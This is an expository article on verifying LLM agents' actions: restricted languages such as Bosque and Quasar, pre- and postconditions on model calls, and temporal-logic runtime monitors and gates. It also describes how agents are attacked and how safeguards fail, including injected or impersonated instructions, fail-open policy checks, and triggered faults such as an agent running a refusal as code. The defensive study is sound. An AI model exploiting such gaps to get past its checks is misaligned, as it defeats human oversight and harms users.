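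Suppose an engineer wants a tool that reads any program and reports whether it can ever pay more than 100 dollars. No such tool can be right about every program. To see why, take any program Q, disable its payments, and add one line at the end:

```
run Q with its payments disabled
transfer(1000, "Tom")
```

The new program breaks the limit if and only if Q finishes. A perfect payment checker would therefore reveal whether Q ever finishes, and Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no algorithm can determine this for every program. Rice's theorem, published in 1953, extends the result to any behaviour that some programs have and others don't.

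A checker for an ordinary language must therefore fail on some programs. It may run forever, stop without an answer, miss an error or raise a false alarm. Scala's capture checker raises false alarms, for example when it rejects a harmless function because it contains a payment in a branch that never runs.

A language with restricted semantics leaves out features that make programs hard to analyse, so that important questions about a program are decidable, meaning that an algorithm always finishes with the right answer. As a result, programmers have to write some programs differently and can't write others at all.

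### Loops, shared data and hidden behaviour

Rice's theorem doesn't explain why checkers struggle with quite simple programs. Marron (2024), in *Toward Programming Languages for Reasoning*, blames seven common features of programming languages, including loops. This loop adds up half of each bill in a list:

```
total = 0
for bill in bills:
    total = total + bill / 2
```

If no bill is negative, `total` can't be negative either. A solver can confirm this for three bills by following the loop three times, but the list could have any length. A proof for every length needs a loop invariant, which is a statement that is true before the loop starts and stays true after each pass. Here "`total` is at least 0" is enough. Longer programs need more complicated invariants, and no general method can always find them.

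Shared data causes a different problem:

```
approved = ["Tom"]
payees = approved
payees.append("Eve")
```

In Python, `approved` now contains Eve too, because both names refer to the same list. The line that added her doesn't mention `approved`. To rely on the list of approved payees, a checker has to consider every line, in every function, that might access the same list under another name.

Some behaviour doesn't appear in the code. Python's `min` function raises an error if the list is empty, which a programmer has to learn from the documentation. An 8-bit integer usually ranges from −128 to 127, so in many languages negating −128 can give −128 again. A checker has to consider such cases everywhere, but people and language models tend to forget them.

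### What Bosque leaves out

Bosque is the programming language at the centre of Marron's 2026 design for agents. It looks much like TypeScript, a popular typed version of JavaScript, but has stricter rules:

| Obstacle | Rule in Bosque |
|---|---|
| Loops need invariants | There are no loops, only library operations on whole lists, such as `map` and `allOf` |
| Data can change under another name | Data values never change, and a program can't test whether two names refer to the same object |
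| Negation can fail | Integer ranges are symmetric, so every number has a negative |
| Results can depend on unstated details, such as how a sort orders ties | Each operation has exactly one possible result for a given input |
| An object can be invalid halfway through an update | An update makes a new object in one step and checks it |

To check that every payment in a list is at most 100 dollars, a Bosque programmer calls `allOf` with that condition. The solver then works with a known operation and doesn't have to infer what a loop computes.

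Bosque also lets programmers put more information into types. An ordinary integer could be a temperature, a price or a number of milliseconds. In Bosque, `Fahrenheit` can be a type of its own, and the compiler rejects code that passes a plain integer where the program needs a temperature. A string type can require a pattern, such as the digits of a postcode. Larger types can carry conditions:

```
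entity TempRange {
    field low: Fahrenheit;
    field high: Fahrenheit;
    invariant $low <= $high;
}
```

Bosque checks that `low` is no higher than `high` whenever a program creates a `TempRange`, so this condition holds in any function that receives one. Separate types for currencies would also stop an agent from paying 22.75 euros instead of 22.75 dollars.

Bosque still allows recursion, in which a function calls itself. Recursion can do everything that loops can, so it brings back the problem of program Q. Programmers must mark recursive functions and calls, and are expected to use list operations for most work. Marron therefore says the translation into decidable logic covers the language "almost entirely".

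### Proving a property of the sign function

This Bosque function returns −1 for negative numbers and 1 for all others (the suffix `i` marks an integer):

```
function sign(x: Int): Int {
    var answer = 1i;
    if (x < 0i) {
        answer = -1i;
    }
    return answer;
}
```

The variable `answer` appears to change, although values in Bosque never do. The compiler treats the two assignments as two separate variables and works out which one each path returns. It can do this because, without loops, each assignment happens at most once per call. The function then becomes a formula in SMT-LIB, the standard input language for SMT solvers:

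```
(define-fun sign ((x Int)) Int
  (let ((answer 1))
    (ite (< x 0) (let ((answer -1)) answer) answer)))
```

Here `ite` means "if, then, else". If x is below 0, the formula uses a new `answer` equal to −1. Otherwise, it uses the original `answer`.

The programmer claims that the result always lies between −1 and 1. Sundew, Bosque's validator, can test the claim by having the solver search for a counterexample:

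```
is there an x such that  NOT (-1 <= sign(x) AND sign(x) <= 1) ?
```

`sign(x)` is −1 if x is negative and 1 if x is zero or positive. Both values are in the range, so the claim holds for every integer. According to Marron, the proof takes 7 milliseconds. Testing every 64-bit integer at a billion per second would take about 585 years.

The property is fairly weak. A sign function normally returns 0 for 0, while this one returns 1, and both versions pass. A function that always returned 0 would pass too.

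### What the size limits leave unproved

The sign function is easy to check partly because its input is a single number. Strings and lists can be any length, and the solver has only a semi-decision procedure for them. If a counterexample exists, the solver will eventually find it, but if none exists, the search may never end. Bosque's validator therefore limits the size of strings and lists in the input. These limits make the problem decidable, but a result of "no counterexample" applies only to inputs within them.

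Suppose an agent splits a bill evenly among friends and rounds each share up to a whole cent. The programmer claims that the shares never exceed the bill by more than 5 cents in total. Rounding adds less than a cent per person, so the claim is true for up to six people, but it can fail for seven. For example, splitting a bill of $45.51 seven ways gives shares of $6.51, which add up to $45.57. A validator that checks only lists of at most six shares would not find this error.

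The method assumes that most bugs show up on some small input, so a search limited to small inputs will catch them. This seems reasonable for ordinary mistakes, but an attacker who knows the limit could look for an input just beyond it that triggers a bug. The 2026 design also checks conditions while the program runs, against the actual list, whatever its length.

The 2024 paper applies the validator to a trading application of about 2,000 lines, published by Morgan Stanley and translated into Bosque. The tool listed every error the program could produce and settled each in under 0.2 seconds. One rule required the stock available for sale to fall whenever the program accepted an order. The solver found that an order with a quantity of −1 broke this rule, because accepting it would increase the stock. The programmer can fix the error by using a type that excludes negative numbers, after which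 the tool finds no small failing input.

This result is useful because the programmer wrote one simple rule and no proof, and got an example to debug. But it concerns only one application. The 2026 paper presents a design with short examples and does not test whether agents that write Bosque make fewer mistakes or finish more tasks. It does show how the validator could help an agent plan, by checking a payment's requirements before the agent adds the payment to its program.

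### Quasar: program logic on one side, effects on the other

*QUASAR* (Mell, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) applies restricted semantics to code actions. Its language separates internal code, which handles only computation and control flow, from external calls, which can affect the world. Developers annotate each external call with its relevant effects, such as which resources it uses.

The internal part is tiny, with `if` and an operation that goes through a finite list once, but no `while` loops or recursion. Every program therefore finishes as long as its external calls do, so program Q can't be written in the internal part.

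Models struggled to write Quasar directly, so they write a restricted form of Python, and a compiler translates it. Suppose an agent has to request money from three roommates:

```
for friend in ["Ana", "Ben", "Cleo"]:
    request_money(friend, 29.75)
```

If each request needs approval, ordinary Python stops three times to wait for the user. Quasar expands the loop into three separate calls. Each has all the information it needs, so Quasar can show them to the user together. If the amount depended on another call, the requests would have to wait for that call's result. Quasar can do its internal calculations in any order because they have no side effects and always give the same answer.

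Mell and colleagues tested Quasar on programs that GPT-5 wrote and found that it reduced approval requests by an average of 26% on AgentDojo, where only 57% of the tasks had calls that it could combine. The reduction was 97% on 80 research questions from BrowseComp-Plus, where agents make many similar calls. However, users may not read every request in a long batch.

The restrictions had little effect on accuracy. On AgentDojo, 63.4% of programs in the restricted Python gave the right answer, compared with 64.5% in full Python. Returning the compiler's error messages to the model for another attempt raised the figure to 67.7%. As in LACUNA, the compiler finds these errors before any of the code runs.

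A small language is also easy to run in unusual ways. In one mode, a Quasar variable can hold a set of possible values. If a model's answer to whether a photograph shows alcohol is uncertain, the variable holds {yes, no}, and Quasar follows both branches of any `if` that depends on it. With thresholds tuned on sample tasks, the final set should contain the right answer at least 90% of the time. This statistical guarantee was not very informative on AgentDojo, because the set contained more than one answer for 84% of tasks.

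Bosque's restrictions help a solver prove properties before a program runs, while Quasar's mainly help the runtime control external calls. These calls can use any Python library, but Quasar can't analyse the code inside, so the developer's annotations are part of the trusted base. If a developer forgets to mark a function that sends email, Quasar may run it without approval.

### Should agents use new languages?

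Armin Ronacher, a software developer known for the Python web framework Flask, makes the case for new languages in *A Language For Agents* (2026). He argues that agents work best when they can understand a piece of code without searching the rest of the project. Many languages let programmers leave out types so that they have less to write, but this matters less when a model writes the code. Ronacher also wants functions to declare the effects they need, such as access to the clock, and a tool to add missing declarations automatically.

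The small number of libraries for a new language used to be a strong reason to avoid it. Ronacher thinks this matters less now that an agent can translate a library from another language, and gives the example of a network driver that an agent rewrote in JavaScript. Marron expects clear units and simple rules to remain useful as models improve, because they help expert programmers too.

One argument for using Python, TypeScript or Rust is that models have seen vast amounts of code in these languages, which Ronacher agrees makes a dramatic difference. People have also had years to find bugs in established compilers and runtimes, while a new language adds a young compiler to the trusted base. Bosque's tools, for example, are still experimental. Popular languages also already offer some restrictions. Rust normally prevents one part of a program from changing data while another part is using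 it.

Familiarity with a language matters less than it did, at least for strong models with good tools. *No Resource, No Benchmarks, No Problem?* (Giagnorio, Martin-Lopez and Bavota, 2026) reports that models solved 0–1% of hard problems in Gleam and MoonBit, two recent languages, compared with 59–89% in Python and Java. But these were older models, such as GPT-4o, and they had one attempt with no documentation or compiler.

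Shen, Cheng and colleagues (2026), in *Bridging the Knowledge Void*, tested newer models on 155 problems in Cangjie, a language that Huawei released in 2024. They compared a single unaided attempt with up to 15 rounds in which the model could search the documentation and run code:

| Model | Solved unaided | Solved with documentation and running code |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 45% | 82% |
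| Qwen3-Max | 8% | 74% |
| DeepSeek-V3.2 | 3% | 63% |

When Qwen3-Max could not run and test code, the second score fell to 54%, so the improvement did not come from documentation alone.

*Frontier Coding Agents Use Metaprogramming to Adapt to Unfamiliar Programming Languages* (Sharma, Thorat and Chopra, 2026) tested coding agents on four deliberately strange languages. One, Brainfuck, has only eight commands, each a single punctuation mark. GPT-5.4 solved 99.7% of the problems across the four languages, Claude Opus 4.6 solved 86.9%, and Kimi K2.5 solved 11.3%. The three models score within a few points of each other on a standard test of fixing bugs in Python projects.

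The two strongest agents, Opus and GPT-5.4, often wrote Python programs to generate code in the strange languages instead of writing it directly. When Sharma and colleagues prohibited this in Brainfuck, Opus fell from 64 problems solved out of 80 to 27, and GPT-5.4 fell from 79 to 29. Brainfuck is far less clear and explicit than a language like Bosque, so these figures probably exaggerate how hard Bosque would be to learn. A written description of the strategy barely helped weaker agents, but a library of working Python helpers raised Claude Sonnet 4.6 from 12 problems to 64. Designers of a new language may therefore help agents more by supplying working code than by writing a longer manual.

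There is less evidence that a language designed for models makes them more accurate. Vera, one such language, requires a contract on every function and replaces variable names with typed references. *VeraBench* (aallan, 2026), by Vera's creator, tests models that learn the language from one document in the prompt. Kimi K2.5 solved all the problems in Vera and 86% in Python. But Claude Opus 4 solved 88% in Vera and 96% in Python, and most of the other models also did better in Python. The test had 50 problems and one run per model, so small differences mean little. In a second run with newer versions of the language and the test, Claude Sonnet 4's Vera score went from 4 points above its TypeScript score to 9 points below it.

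Extending Python is a compromise that leaves the obstacles to analysis in place. *Agent-Native by Design* (Dantanarayana, Kashmira and colleagues, 2026) presents Jac, which adds model calls and workflows to Python. The programmer declares which steps can follow which, and the model chooses only among them. Coding agents used about half as many tokens to build five applications in Jac as with OpenAI's standard programming library. Jac's developers, who wrote the paper, aim for less work and faster programs rather than proof. Jac also keeps Python's loops and shared data, so a checker for the whole language would face the same difficulties as one for Python. Quasar suits checking better because the model writes familiar code but can use only the part of Python that the compiler accepts.

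Another option is to keep features that are hard to analyse, such as loops, and have LLMs do the proof work. Willison (2025) relays the computer scientist Martin Kleppmann's argument that LLMs will bring existing verification tools into common use, including Dafny, Nagini for Python and Verus for Rust. These tools can handle loops, but the programmer usually has to supply the invariants. If LLMs can supply them reliably, there is less reason to ban loops. An agent that writes a new program for each task would still benefit from a check that takes milliseconds and needs no help with proofs.

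The choice of translator also matters. In *TrustedCode* (2026), a language model translates Python into WhyML, a language for verification, and adds contracts. An automatic prover then checks the result, and any errors go back to the model. Bosque and Quasar translate with fixed compilers, which engineers can test once and reuse, whereas a model might translate each program differently. If the model leaves out a payment, the prover can correctly show that the WhyML version stays under the $100 limit even though the Python program exceeds it.

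## Preconditions and postconditions on single actions

A restricted language makes programs easier to analyse, but a solver still needs a statement to prove. For a single action, that statement is usually a contract, with a precondition that must hold before the action and a postcondition that must hold after it. The 100 dollar limit on payments is a precondition. Contracts long predate language models, and most of the theory still applies to agents, but a model call violates one of its main assumptions.

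### The Hoare triple

Hoare, in *An Axiomatic Basis for Computer Programming* (1969), introduced a notation for contracts that computer scientists now write like this:

```
{P} C {Q}
```

This Hoare triple means that if P is true before command C runs, and C finishes successfully, then Q is true afterwards. For example:

```
{bill <= 200}   amount = bill / 2   {amount <= 100}
```

With Hoare's rule for assignments, a programmer can find the precondition mechanically by replacing `amount` in the postcondition, `amount <= 100`, with the expression assigned to it. The result is `bill / 2 <= 100`, which is the same as `bill <= 200`. Another rule chains commands together when the postcondition of one is the precondition of the next. With a few such rules, a programmer can prove a property of a whole program without running it.

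The triple does not promise that the command will finish. A program that always stops with an error satisfies any postcondition.

*Applying "Design by Contract"* (Meyer, 1992) uses preconditions and postconditions to divide responsibility between the parts of a program. Meyer compares a function to a courier in Paris, and the code that calls it to a customer. The customer must hand over a package of at most 5 kilograms and pay 100 francs, and the courier must then deliver it within four hours. If the precondition is false, the caller has a bug, and if the postcondition is false, the function has one. Meyer therefore opposes checking the same condition on both sides, which makes programs more complicated, and treats run-time checking as optional.

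This division of labour assumes that somebody can fix a faulty caller. When the caller is a model, a developer can't simply correct the bug, and an attacker may have caused it. So the function, or the harness in front of it, has to check the precondition on every call.

### When the command is a model call

Suppose the program asks a model to do the division:

```
{bill <= 200}   amount = ask_model("What is half of the bill?", message)   {amount <= 100}
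```

The assignment rule no longer helps, because there is no expression to substitute for `amount`. The model may return 22.75 or 1,000, and no condition on the bill rules out the second answer. Weng, Wang and colleagues (2026) write in *When Code Becomes an LLM Call* that the postcondition of a model call "never holds by construction; it holds only where the program checks it".

A check after the call restores the guarantee:

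```
amount = ask_model("What is half of the bill?", message)
if not (0 < amount <= 100):  stop
{0 < amount <= 100}
```

If the program gets past the second line, the check guarantees that the amount is in the range, whatever the model returned. It doesn't show that the amount is half of the bill, because the program never had the bill as a number to compare it with.

*ToolGate* (Liu, Peng and colleagues, 2026) applies the same idea to tool results. It keeps a table of trusted facts. A tool can run only if the table satisfies the tool's precondition, and the result enters the table only if it satisfies the postcondition. This works well for lookups, because a malformed bank balance never becomes a trusted fact. It is riskier for payments. If the bank moves the money but returns a garbled receipt, ToolGate discards the receipt and leaves the table unchanged, so the agent may pay again. A postcondition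 can detect a problem with an irreversible action only after the action has happened, so preventing such problems depends mostly on the precondition.

With GPT-5.2, ToolGate completed 45.5% of the repository-management tasks in the MCP-Universe benchmark, compared with 39.4% for the best of five other methods. These percentages match 15 and 13 tasks out of 33, so the difference is small. ToolGate also has its own tool search, and the comparison doesn't separate the effect of the search from that of the contracts.

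### Bosque's contract for a payment

A function in Bosque can carry its contract in its definition. In simplified notation, Marron's contract for `transfer` is:

```
transfer(amount, payer, payee)
    condition 1:   amount > 0
    condition 2:   amount <= limit
                   OR the event log contains Approve(payee, amount)
```

The first condition requires a positive amount. Without it, a bank's software might treat a payment of −$22.75 to Tom as an instruction to take money from him. The second condition lets a payment exceed the limit only if the user has approved that amount for that payee. The agent can't edit the log, so the model can't invent an approval.

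With a limit of 100 dollars, the contract has these results:

| Payment requested | Approval in the log | Result |
|---|---|---|
| 22.75 to Tom | None | Allowed |
| −22.75 to Tom | None | Refused |
| 1,000 to Tom | None | Refused |
| 1,000 to Tom | 1,000 to Tom | Allowed |
| 1,000 to Tom | 900 to Tom | Refused |
| 1,000 to Eve | 1,000 to Tom | Refused |
| 1,000 to Tom, for the second time | 1,000 to Tom, once | Allowed |

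The last result is probably not what the user wants. The condition tests only whether the log contains an approval, and approvals stay in the log, so one approval covers any number of identical payments. The agent could also make ten payments of 99 dollars with no approval. Preventing both problems requires a rule that counts or adds up payments over the whole run.

The contract also has no postcondition, so it relies on the bank to move the right amount once the call goes through.

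### Checking while the code runs and before

Marron's runtime tests both conditions on every call to `transfer`. If either is false, the runtime aborts the task before any money moves. The test uses the real amount and log, so its result is definite, but it happens only when the agent calls `transfer`. By then the agent may already have told Tom that the money is on its way.

A solver can find the problem before the script starts, as in the first section's example of a script that passes the model's answer straight to `transfer`. With Bosque's contract, the log is unknown as well as the amount:

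```
is there an amount a and a log L such that
    NOT (0 < a  AND  (a <= 100 OR L contains Approve(Tom, a))) ?
```

An amount of 1,000 with an empty log is one solution. The validator in Marron's example therefore reports that it cannot ensure the second condition. It should report the first as well, since the script would also pass on an amount of −5, but the sample message leaves this out. The agent can repair the script by adding two lines:

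```
if a <= 0:    stop
if a > 100:   ask the user to approve paying a to Tom; stop if refused
transfer(a, Tom)
```

An amount of zero or less no longer reaches `transfer`. A positive amount up to 100 satisfies both conditions. A larger amount reaches `transfer` only after the runtime has recorded the approval, so the solver finds no counterexample. Logs can be any length, so Bosque's size limits may apply to this result too.

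Marron argues that a report like this is better feedback than a failed test. A test shows one bad input, and an agent may change the script to handle only that input. But the run-time check is still necessary, because it also covers scripts that nobody has analysed.

### Requested, checked or impossible

Weng and colleagues sort constraints into three levels of assurance according to what it takes to break them. Suppose the agent may pay only Tom:

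| Level | How the developer applies the rule | What breaks it |
|---|---|---|
| Prompt-only | The prompt tells the model to pay only Tom | A model error or an injected instruction |
| Code-checked | `transfer` compares the payee with Tom's account | A bug in the check |
| Capability-bound | The agent has only a `pay_tom` function | Nothing, according to Weng and colleagues |

A tool left off the list in the prompt is still in the program, so an agent may still be able to call it. Goose, a general-purpose agent, accepted calls to tools it had never offered the model. Another agent, JARVIS, picked a tool from outside its list of candidates in all five tests, with no attacker involved, because the model made up tool names that happened to exist in the full catalogue. To make an action impossible, a developer has to remove it from the code that executes calls.

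### What 496 model calls check

Weng and colleagues applied these ideas to 40 popular open-source agent systems, including Codex and Google's Gemini CLI. They found 496 places where a program calls a model and acts on the reply. About 48% of the models' outputs could steer what the program did next or run as code, and in 73% of those cases no person saw the output before it took effect.

A missing check leaves no trace in the code, so the researchers needed a separate standard for what each call should check. They had GPT-5.6 Sol produce one in four steps, each with a fresh context:

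1. An agent read the code and described the purpose of the call, leaving out how the program currently checks it.
2. Another agent saw only this description and listed the constraints that the call needs. For each one, it had to give a failure that would occur without the constraint.
3. Another agent saw only the code and listed the constraints that the program enforces.
4. A last agent compared the two lists.

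The programs checked something both before and after 82% of the calls. But 63% of the expected constraints were unmet, and only 5.3% of the calls met their whole contract. For most of the unmet constraints, the program had a relevant check, but it covered only some values or some paths through the code. The programs had no relevant check for 15% of the expected constraints.

The 5.3% figure mostly follows from the 63% figure, though it sounds much worse. If a call needs four constraints and the program has an independent 37% chance of meeting each one, it will meet all four only about 2% of the time.

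The programs were better at checking the form of a reply than its meaning. STORM, which writes research articles, uses a model to judge whether a topic is appropriate and rejects the topic only if the reply starts with "No", so a lowercase "no" or a refusal to answer counts as approval. Gemini CLI has an optional check that uses a model to judge whether a tool call follows a security policy. This check fails open, meaning that the code allows the call if the reply is empty or unreadable, or if the request fails. In Skyvern, which controls a web browser, the policy check correctly denied a click, but the code that performs clicks never read the decision.

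Developers also left many rules to the model. Of the constraints that concerned the prompt, 67% were prompt-only. Across all phases, 268 prompt-only constraints were about format, such as the maximum length of a list. A line or two of code could have tested such constraints.

Some contract software can fail open by design. *A DbC Inspired Neurosymbolic Layer for Trustworthy Agent Design* (Leoveanu-Condrei, 2025) wraps every model call in a contract and has the model correct answers that break it, up to a set number of attempts. If the last answer still breaks the contract, the program continues and may return either a safe default or the unchecked output. That may be acceptable for a draft email, but an unchecked payment could send the 1,000 dollars that Tom mentioned as a joke.

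### How much the missing checks matter

Weng and colleagues excluded 83% of the 1,697 unmet constraints as harmless to security, for example because a later check would stop a bad reply or because the constraint went unmet before there was a reply. In 114 cases, enforcing the missing constraint would block or narrow a route to real harm. These cases came from 60 separate faults, and the researchers triggered 38 of them.

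One of the 38 was in CodeWhale, a coding agent that runs part of a model's reply as Python whenever the reply contains a certain marker. In one test, the model mentioned the marker while refusing an attacker's request, and CodeWhale ran two fragments of the refusal as code.

The researchers then wrote fixes of between 1 and 366 lines that enforced the missing constraints. The fixes stopped the original exploit for all 38 faults, but a variation still worked in three cases, and the researchers count only 23 as completely blocked. Fully blocking some of the others requires judging meaning, which simple pattern matching can't do.

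For 15 of the 22 faults that never triggered, the model or its provider's safety system had declined to produce the harmful reply. A developer who switches to another model could lose that protection without changing any code.

The main weakness of the study is that a model wrote the standard. Three people reviewed its work, making 17,428 judgements in total, but all three were co-authors of the paper. Two of them independently assessed the expected constraints without seeing the code, and their agreement was 0.95 on a scale where 1 is perfect. However, they accepted nearly everything, which makes agreement easy. Cohen's kappa, which corrects more heavily for this, was only 0.60. Kappa can be misleadingly low when one answer dominates, as Weng and colleagues point out, but even perfect agreement wouldn't show that the reviewers were strict enough with plausible drafts, and every unnecessary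 constraint they accepted could raise the 63%.

The researchers have good evidence that the standard wasn't copied from the code, since 15% of its constraints had no counterpart there. But this doesn't show that all the constraints were needed. Yu and colleagues avoided the problem in their customer-service tests by writing separate reference rules by hand, 16 for the airline and 11 for the shop. Doing this for 496 calls would take far more work.

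The 38 triggered faults are stronger evidence than the percentages because in each case a program acted on a bad reply, which is true whether or not one accepts the standard. They show that the faults are real, but not how common they are in practice, because the tests used a single substitute model and up to ten phrasings of each attack.

### Testing commands before they run

Preconditions can also catch accidental errors. Coding agents often try to open files that don't exist or import packages that aren't installed. In *StateMirror*, Shan, Huo and colleagues (2026) found at least one such call in 44% of 4,398 recorded runs. When the agent recovered, it typically needed three more steps and 22,400 tokens.

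StateMirror works out what an action assumes and tests those assumptions without running the action. If an agent requests the test `test_tokenize` in the file `test_sqlparse.py`, StateMirror checks that the file exists and contains a test with that name. The researchers compared it with language models acting as judges on 2,508 actions that people had labelled:

| Method | Warnings that were correct | Bad actions caught | Median time |
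|---|---|---|---|
| StateMirror | 94.0% | 72.2% | 1.5 milliseconds |
| Qwen3.7 Plus, the best judge overall | 69.4% | 53.5% | 17.7 seconds |

In live use on 79 tasks where such mistakes had occurred, StateMirror cut the agent's running time by 15.8% and its token use by 11.8%, and the agent solved as many tasks as before.

When StateMirror can't determine whether an assumption holds, it allows the action. This is reasonable here because a missed mistake usually leads to only a few extra steps. A check on payments should block the payment in that case.

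*Look Before You Leap* (Althoubi, 2026) tested a similar checker on 9,930 shell commands, four fifths of them deliberately broken. The checker caught 95.8% of the broken commands and wrongly flagged 10.0% of the valid ones. Every false alarm came from the check on command options, which relies on each tool's help text and misses some real options. The checks on syntax and on whether the program exists raised no false alarms. They caught half of the broken commands, but only because half had errors of those two kinds, and real agents may make a different mix of mistakes.

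Althoubi's tests on file edits are more worrying, because a bad edit can succeed without any error. If an agent decides to replace lines 40 to 52 and someone adds a line near the top of the file before the edit runs, the edit overwrites the wrong lines. In the tests, a shift of one line made edits by line number silently corrupt 99.1% of files. Edits that quoted the old code never changed the wrong place, as long as the software refused any quotation that didn't match exactly one place in the file.

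The quoted code is a precondition inside the action, since the edit applies only if the file still contains that text. This kind of check also blocks some good edits. Althoubi's own tool, which tolerates small differences in the quotation, made one silent error in 8,320 trials. But it applied only 51% of the single edits to changed files, compared with 98% for a looser method that went wrong 2.3% of the time.

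These checks establish that an action can be carried out as written, but Althoubi notes that it may still be the wrong action.

### Which Tom?

A payment of $22.75 to the wrong Tom meets both of Bosque's conditions. To refuse it, the contract would need another line:

```
requires payee == right_friend;
```

Nothing in the program defines `right_friend`, so the contract can't enforce "pays the right friend" unless some data available to the program determines who that is. Hoare's method has the same limit. It can prove that a program does what its user intends only if someone can state that intention in terms of the program's variables.

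In Marron's example, the program gets the payee by looking up "Tom" in the user's contacts. The contract could require exactly one match, which would detect an ambiguous name but not resolve it. *Agentic Behavior Engineering* (Song, 2026) gives contracts a separate entry for such cases, which tells the agent to ask the user when a name could refer to several people or things. Song also distinguishes a search that finds nothing from a search that fails. If the address book stops responding after returning one Tom, the program hasn't established that there is only one.

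The message may settle the question, because it comes from a particular phone number or account:

```
requires payee == contacts.account_of(message.sender);
```

The harness can check this formula, and it gives the right answer for the lunch payment if the messaging service identifies senders reliably. But suppose Tom Reed writes, "Tom Baker paid for lunch, so send it to him." The formula then blocks the correct payment and allows a payment to Tom Reed, because the correct recipient is named in the text of the message, which only a model or a person can interpret.

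The amount causes a similar problem. The contract can require that the message contain exactly one sum of money and that the payment be half of it. This would reject a payment of the full $45.50, as well as any payment based on Tom's joke, which mentions two sums. But if Tom writes, "lunch was $45.50, but you only had soup", half may not be fair.

The remaining option is to let the user decide. For every payment to a new payee, the contract could require a logged approval from the user, who would see the payee's full name and account number on the screen. "The right friend" then means "the account that the user approved". The runtime can check this as a formula, but it can't check whether the user noticed which Tom the account belonged to.

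## Rules over whole runs, and what happens after an action is blocked

A contract on `transfer` checks one payment at a time, so ten payments of 99 dollars all pass a 100 dollar limit. Two permitted actions can also be harmful in sequence. Suppose a message that appears to be from Tom gives a new account number. The agent is allowed to update the user's contacts and to pay Tom, who is an approved payee, so it updates his entry and then sends him 22.75 dollars. If someone impersonating Tom wrote the message, the money goes to a thief. Banning either action would make the agent much less useful, so the rule has to be about their order. After a payee's account details change, the agent may not pay that person until the user has confirmed the new details.

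### One formula and a five-action trace

Temporal logic is a notation for rules about the order of events. Xiao, Liu and Nuzzo (2026), in *Symbolic Temporal Supervision of LLM Agents Using Contracts*, use a version for finite traces, which suits agents because every session ends. Three of its operators are enough for many rules:

```
ALWAYS p        p is true at this step and every later one
EVENTUALLY p    p is true at this step or a later one
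p UNTIL q       q is true at some step, and p is true at every step before it
```

For a customer-service agent, "no refund before identity is verified" becomes:

```
(NOT refund UNTIL verified)  OR  (ALWAYS NOT refund)
```

The left half is true if the agent verifies the customer's identity at some point and gives no refund before then. The right half is true if the agent never gives a refund. Without it, a run in which the customer only asks about opening hours would violate the rule, because UNTIL requires the verification to happen.

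Software can translate the formula into an automaton, a machine with a fixed set of states that changes state as it reads each action. This one needs three states: waiting, verified and violated. A runtime monitor runs the automaton alongside the agent. To turn the monitor into a gate, the harness works out which state a proposed action would lead to, and refuses the action if the answer is "violated". Here is the gate at work on five proposed actions:

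| Step | Proposed action | What happens | State afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Look up the order | The order is found | Waiting |
| 2 | Verify identity | The postcode does not match | Waiting |
| 3 | Refund the order | The gate refuses | Waiting |
| 4 | Verify identity | The postcode matches | Verified |
| 5 | Refund the order | The customer gets the money | Verified |

At step 2 the agent calls the right tool, but the state changes only when the tool reports a match. At step 3 the agent attempts a refund that never takes place. *One Monitor Does Not Fit All* (Ferrando, 2026) explains why the difference between an attempt and an effect matters. If the monitor counted the attempt as a violation, it would stay in the "violated" state, and the harness would refuse the legitimate refund at step 5. Resetting the monitor after each refusal could erase facts it still needs, such as a withdrawn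 approval. Ferrando's gate instead checks each proposed action against the actions that took effect, while a separate audit record can keep the refused attempts.

The formula has a gap, because the agent could verify Ana's identity and then refund Ben. Closing it takes a rule with a variable, "for every customer c, no refund to c before c is verified", and a monitor that keeps a separate state for each customer. Limits on totals need counters. Ray (2026), in *What Can Be Enforced?*, gives the example of a daily cap for each recipient:

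```
allow transfer(payee, amount) only if
    paid_today[payee] + amount <= 100
```

The second payment of 99 dollars to Tom now fails. An agent could still spread its payments over several people, so a careful developer would also cap the total across all recipients.

Counters also create a timing problem. If a harness runs two tool calls in parallel, it may check two 60-dollar payments against a total of zero and allow both, even if together they exceed the limit. Ferrando's proof that a gate prevents violations therefore requires the harness to check and carry out one action at a time.

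### Blocking cannot make something happen

The refund rule is a safety property. A liveness property requires that something good eventually happens, as in "every payment is eventually followed by a confirmation":

```
ALWAYS (pay IMPLIES EVENTUALLY confirm)
```

Ray proves that a gate that decides before each irreversible action, and never interferes with a run that obeys the rule, can enforce a rule exactly when the rule is a safety property and the gate can recognise every trace that has not yet broken it. The confirmation rule does not meet these conditions. If the gate allows a payment, the agent may never confirm it, and the gate cannot reverse the payment. Refusing the payment would interfere with an agent that was about to confirm it.

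A more powerful enforcer could hold the payment until the confirmation arrives and then release both. This doesn't work when the confirmation depends on the payment, for example because it must include the bank's receipt number.

Developers can often replace a liveness rule with a safety rule. For example, if the rule is that the next action after a payment must be the confirmation, the gate can block any other action. But the agent can still do nothing, and then the session ends with the payment unconfirmed.

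ContrAgent, a system by Xiao and colleagues, handles such open obligations but does not claim to enforce them. Each contract pairs an assumption about the environment with a guarantee about the agent. For example, if the policy service supplies valid refund limits, the agent must stay within them. This separates the agent's failures from those of the services around it. A contract stays ACTIVE while neither the assumption nor the guarantee has permanently failed, even if the agent still owes an action. When the session is about to end, ContrAgent reminds the agent of every open obligation. If the agent still does not act, the status becomes FAIL. The user therefore gets a reliable verdict, but no guarantee that the agent sends the confirmation.

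Xiao and colleagues tested the safety rules on SOPBench, a set of customer-service tasks in seven fields such as banking and healthcare. Some requests are allowed by the written procedure and others are not. With Gemini 2.5 Flash as the agent, the results were:

| Method | Allowed requests completed | Forbidden requests blocked |
|---|---|---|
| No rules | 91% | 32% |
| Rules in the prompt | 64% | 94% |
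| A second model judging each call | 24% | 98% |
| ContrAgent | 90% | 98% |

The prompted agent did worst on tasks with ten or more constraints, where it completed 18% of the allowed requests. ContrAgent completed at least 77% at every level of complexity.

The benchmark suits this method well because it supplies its procedures as structured constraints, so the researchers largely avoided the errors that come from translating prose into logic. Two of the three authors also work at Sponsio Labs, and ContrAgent grew out of that company's software. Still, the comparison shows that a gate can block nearly all forbidden requests with almost no loss of useful work, provided the rules are precise and the agent handles refusals well. On the healthcare tasks, completion fell from 90% to 83% because the agent did not try again after a refusal, even though it was allowed to.

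### What a trace has to record

A monitor can apply a rule about approvals only if the trace records approvals. *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues, 2026) tests how much this matters by replaying recorded runs through MonPoly, an established monitoring program. The runs came mainly from AgentDojo and STAC, a collection of 483 attacks that reach a harmful result through a chain of calls that look harmless individually.

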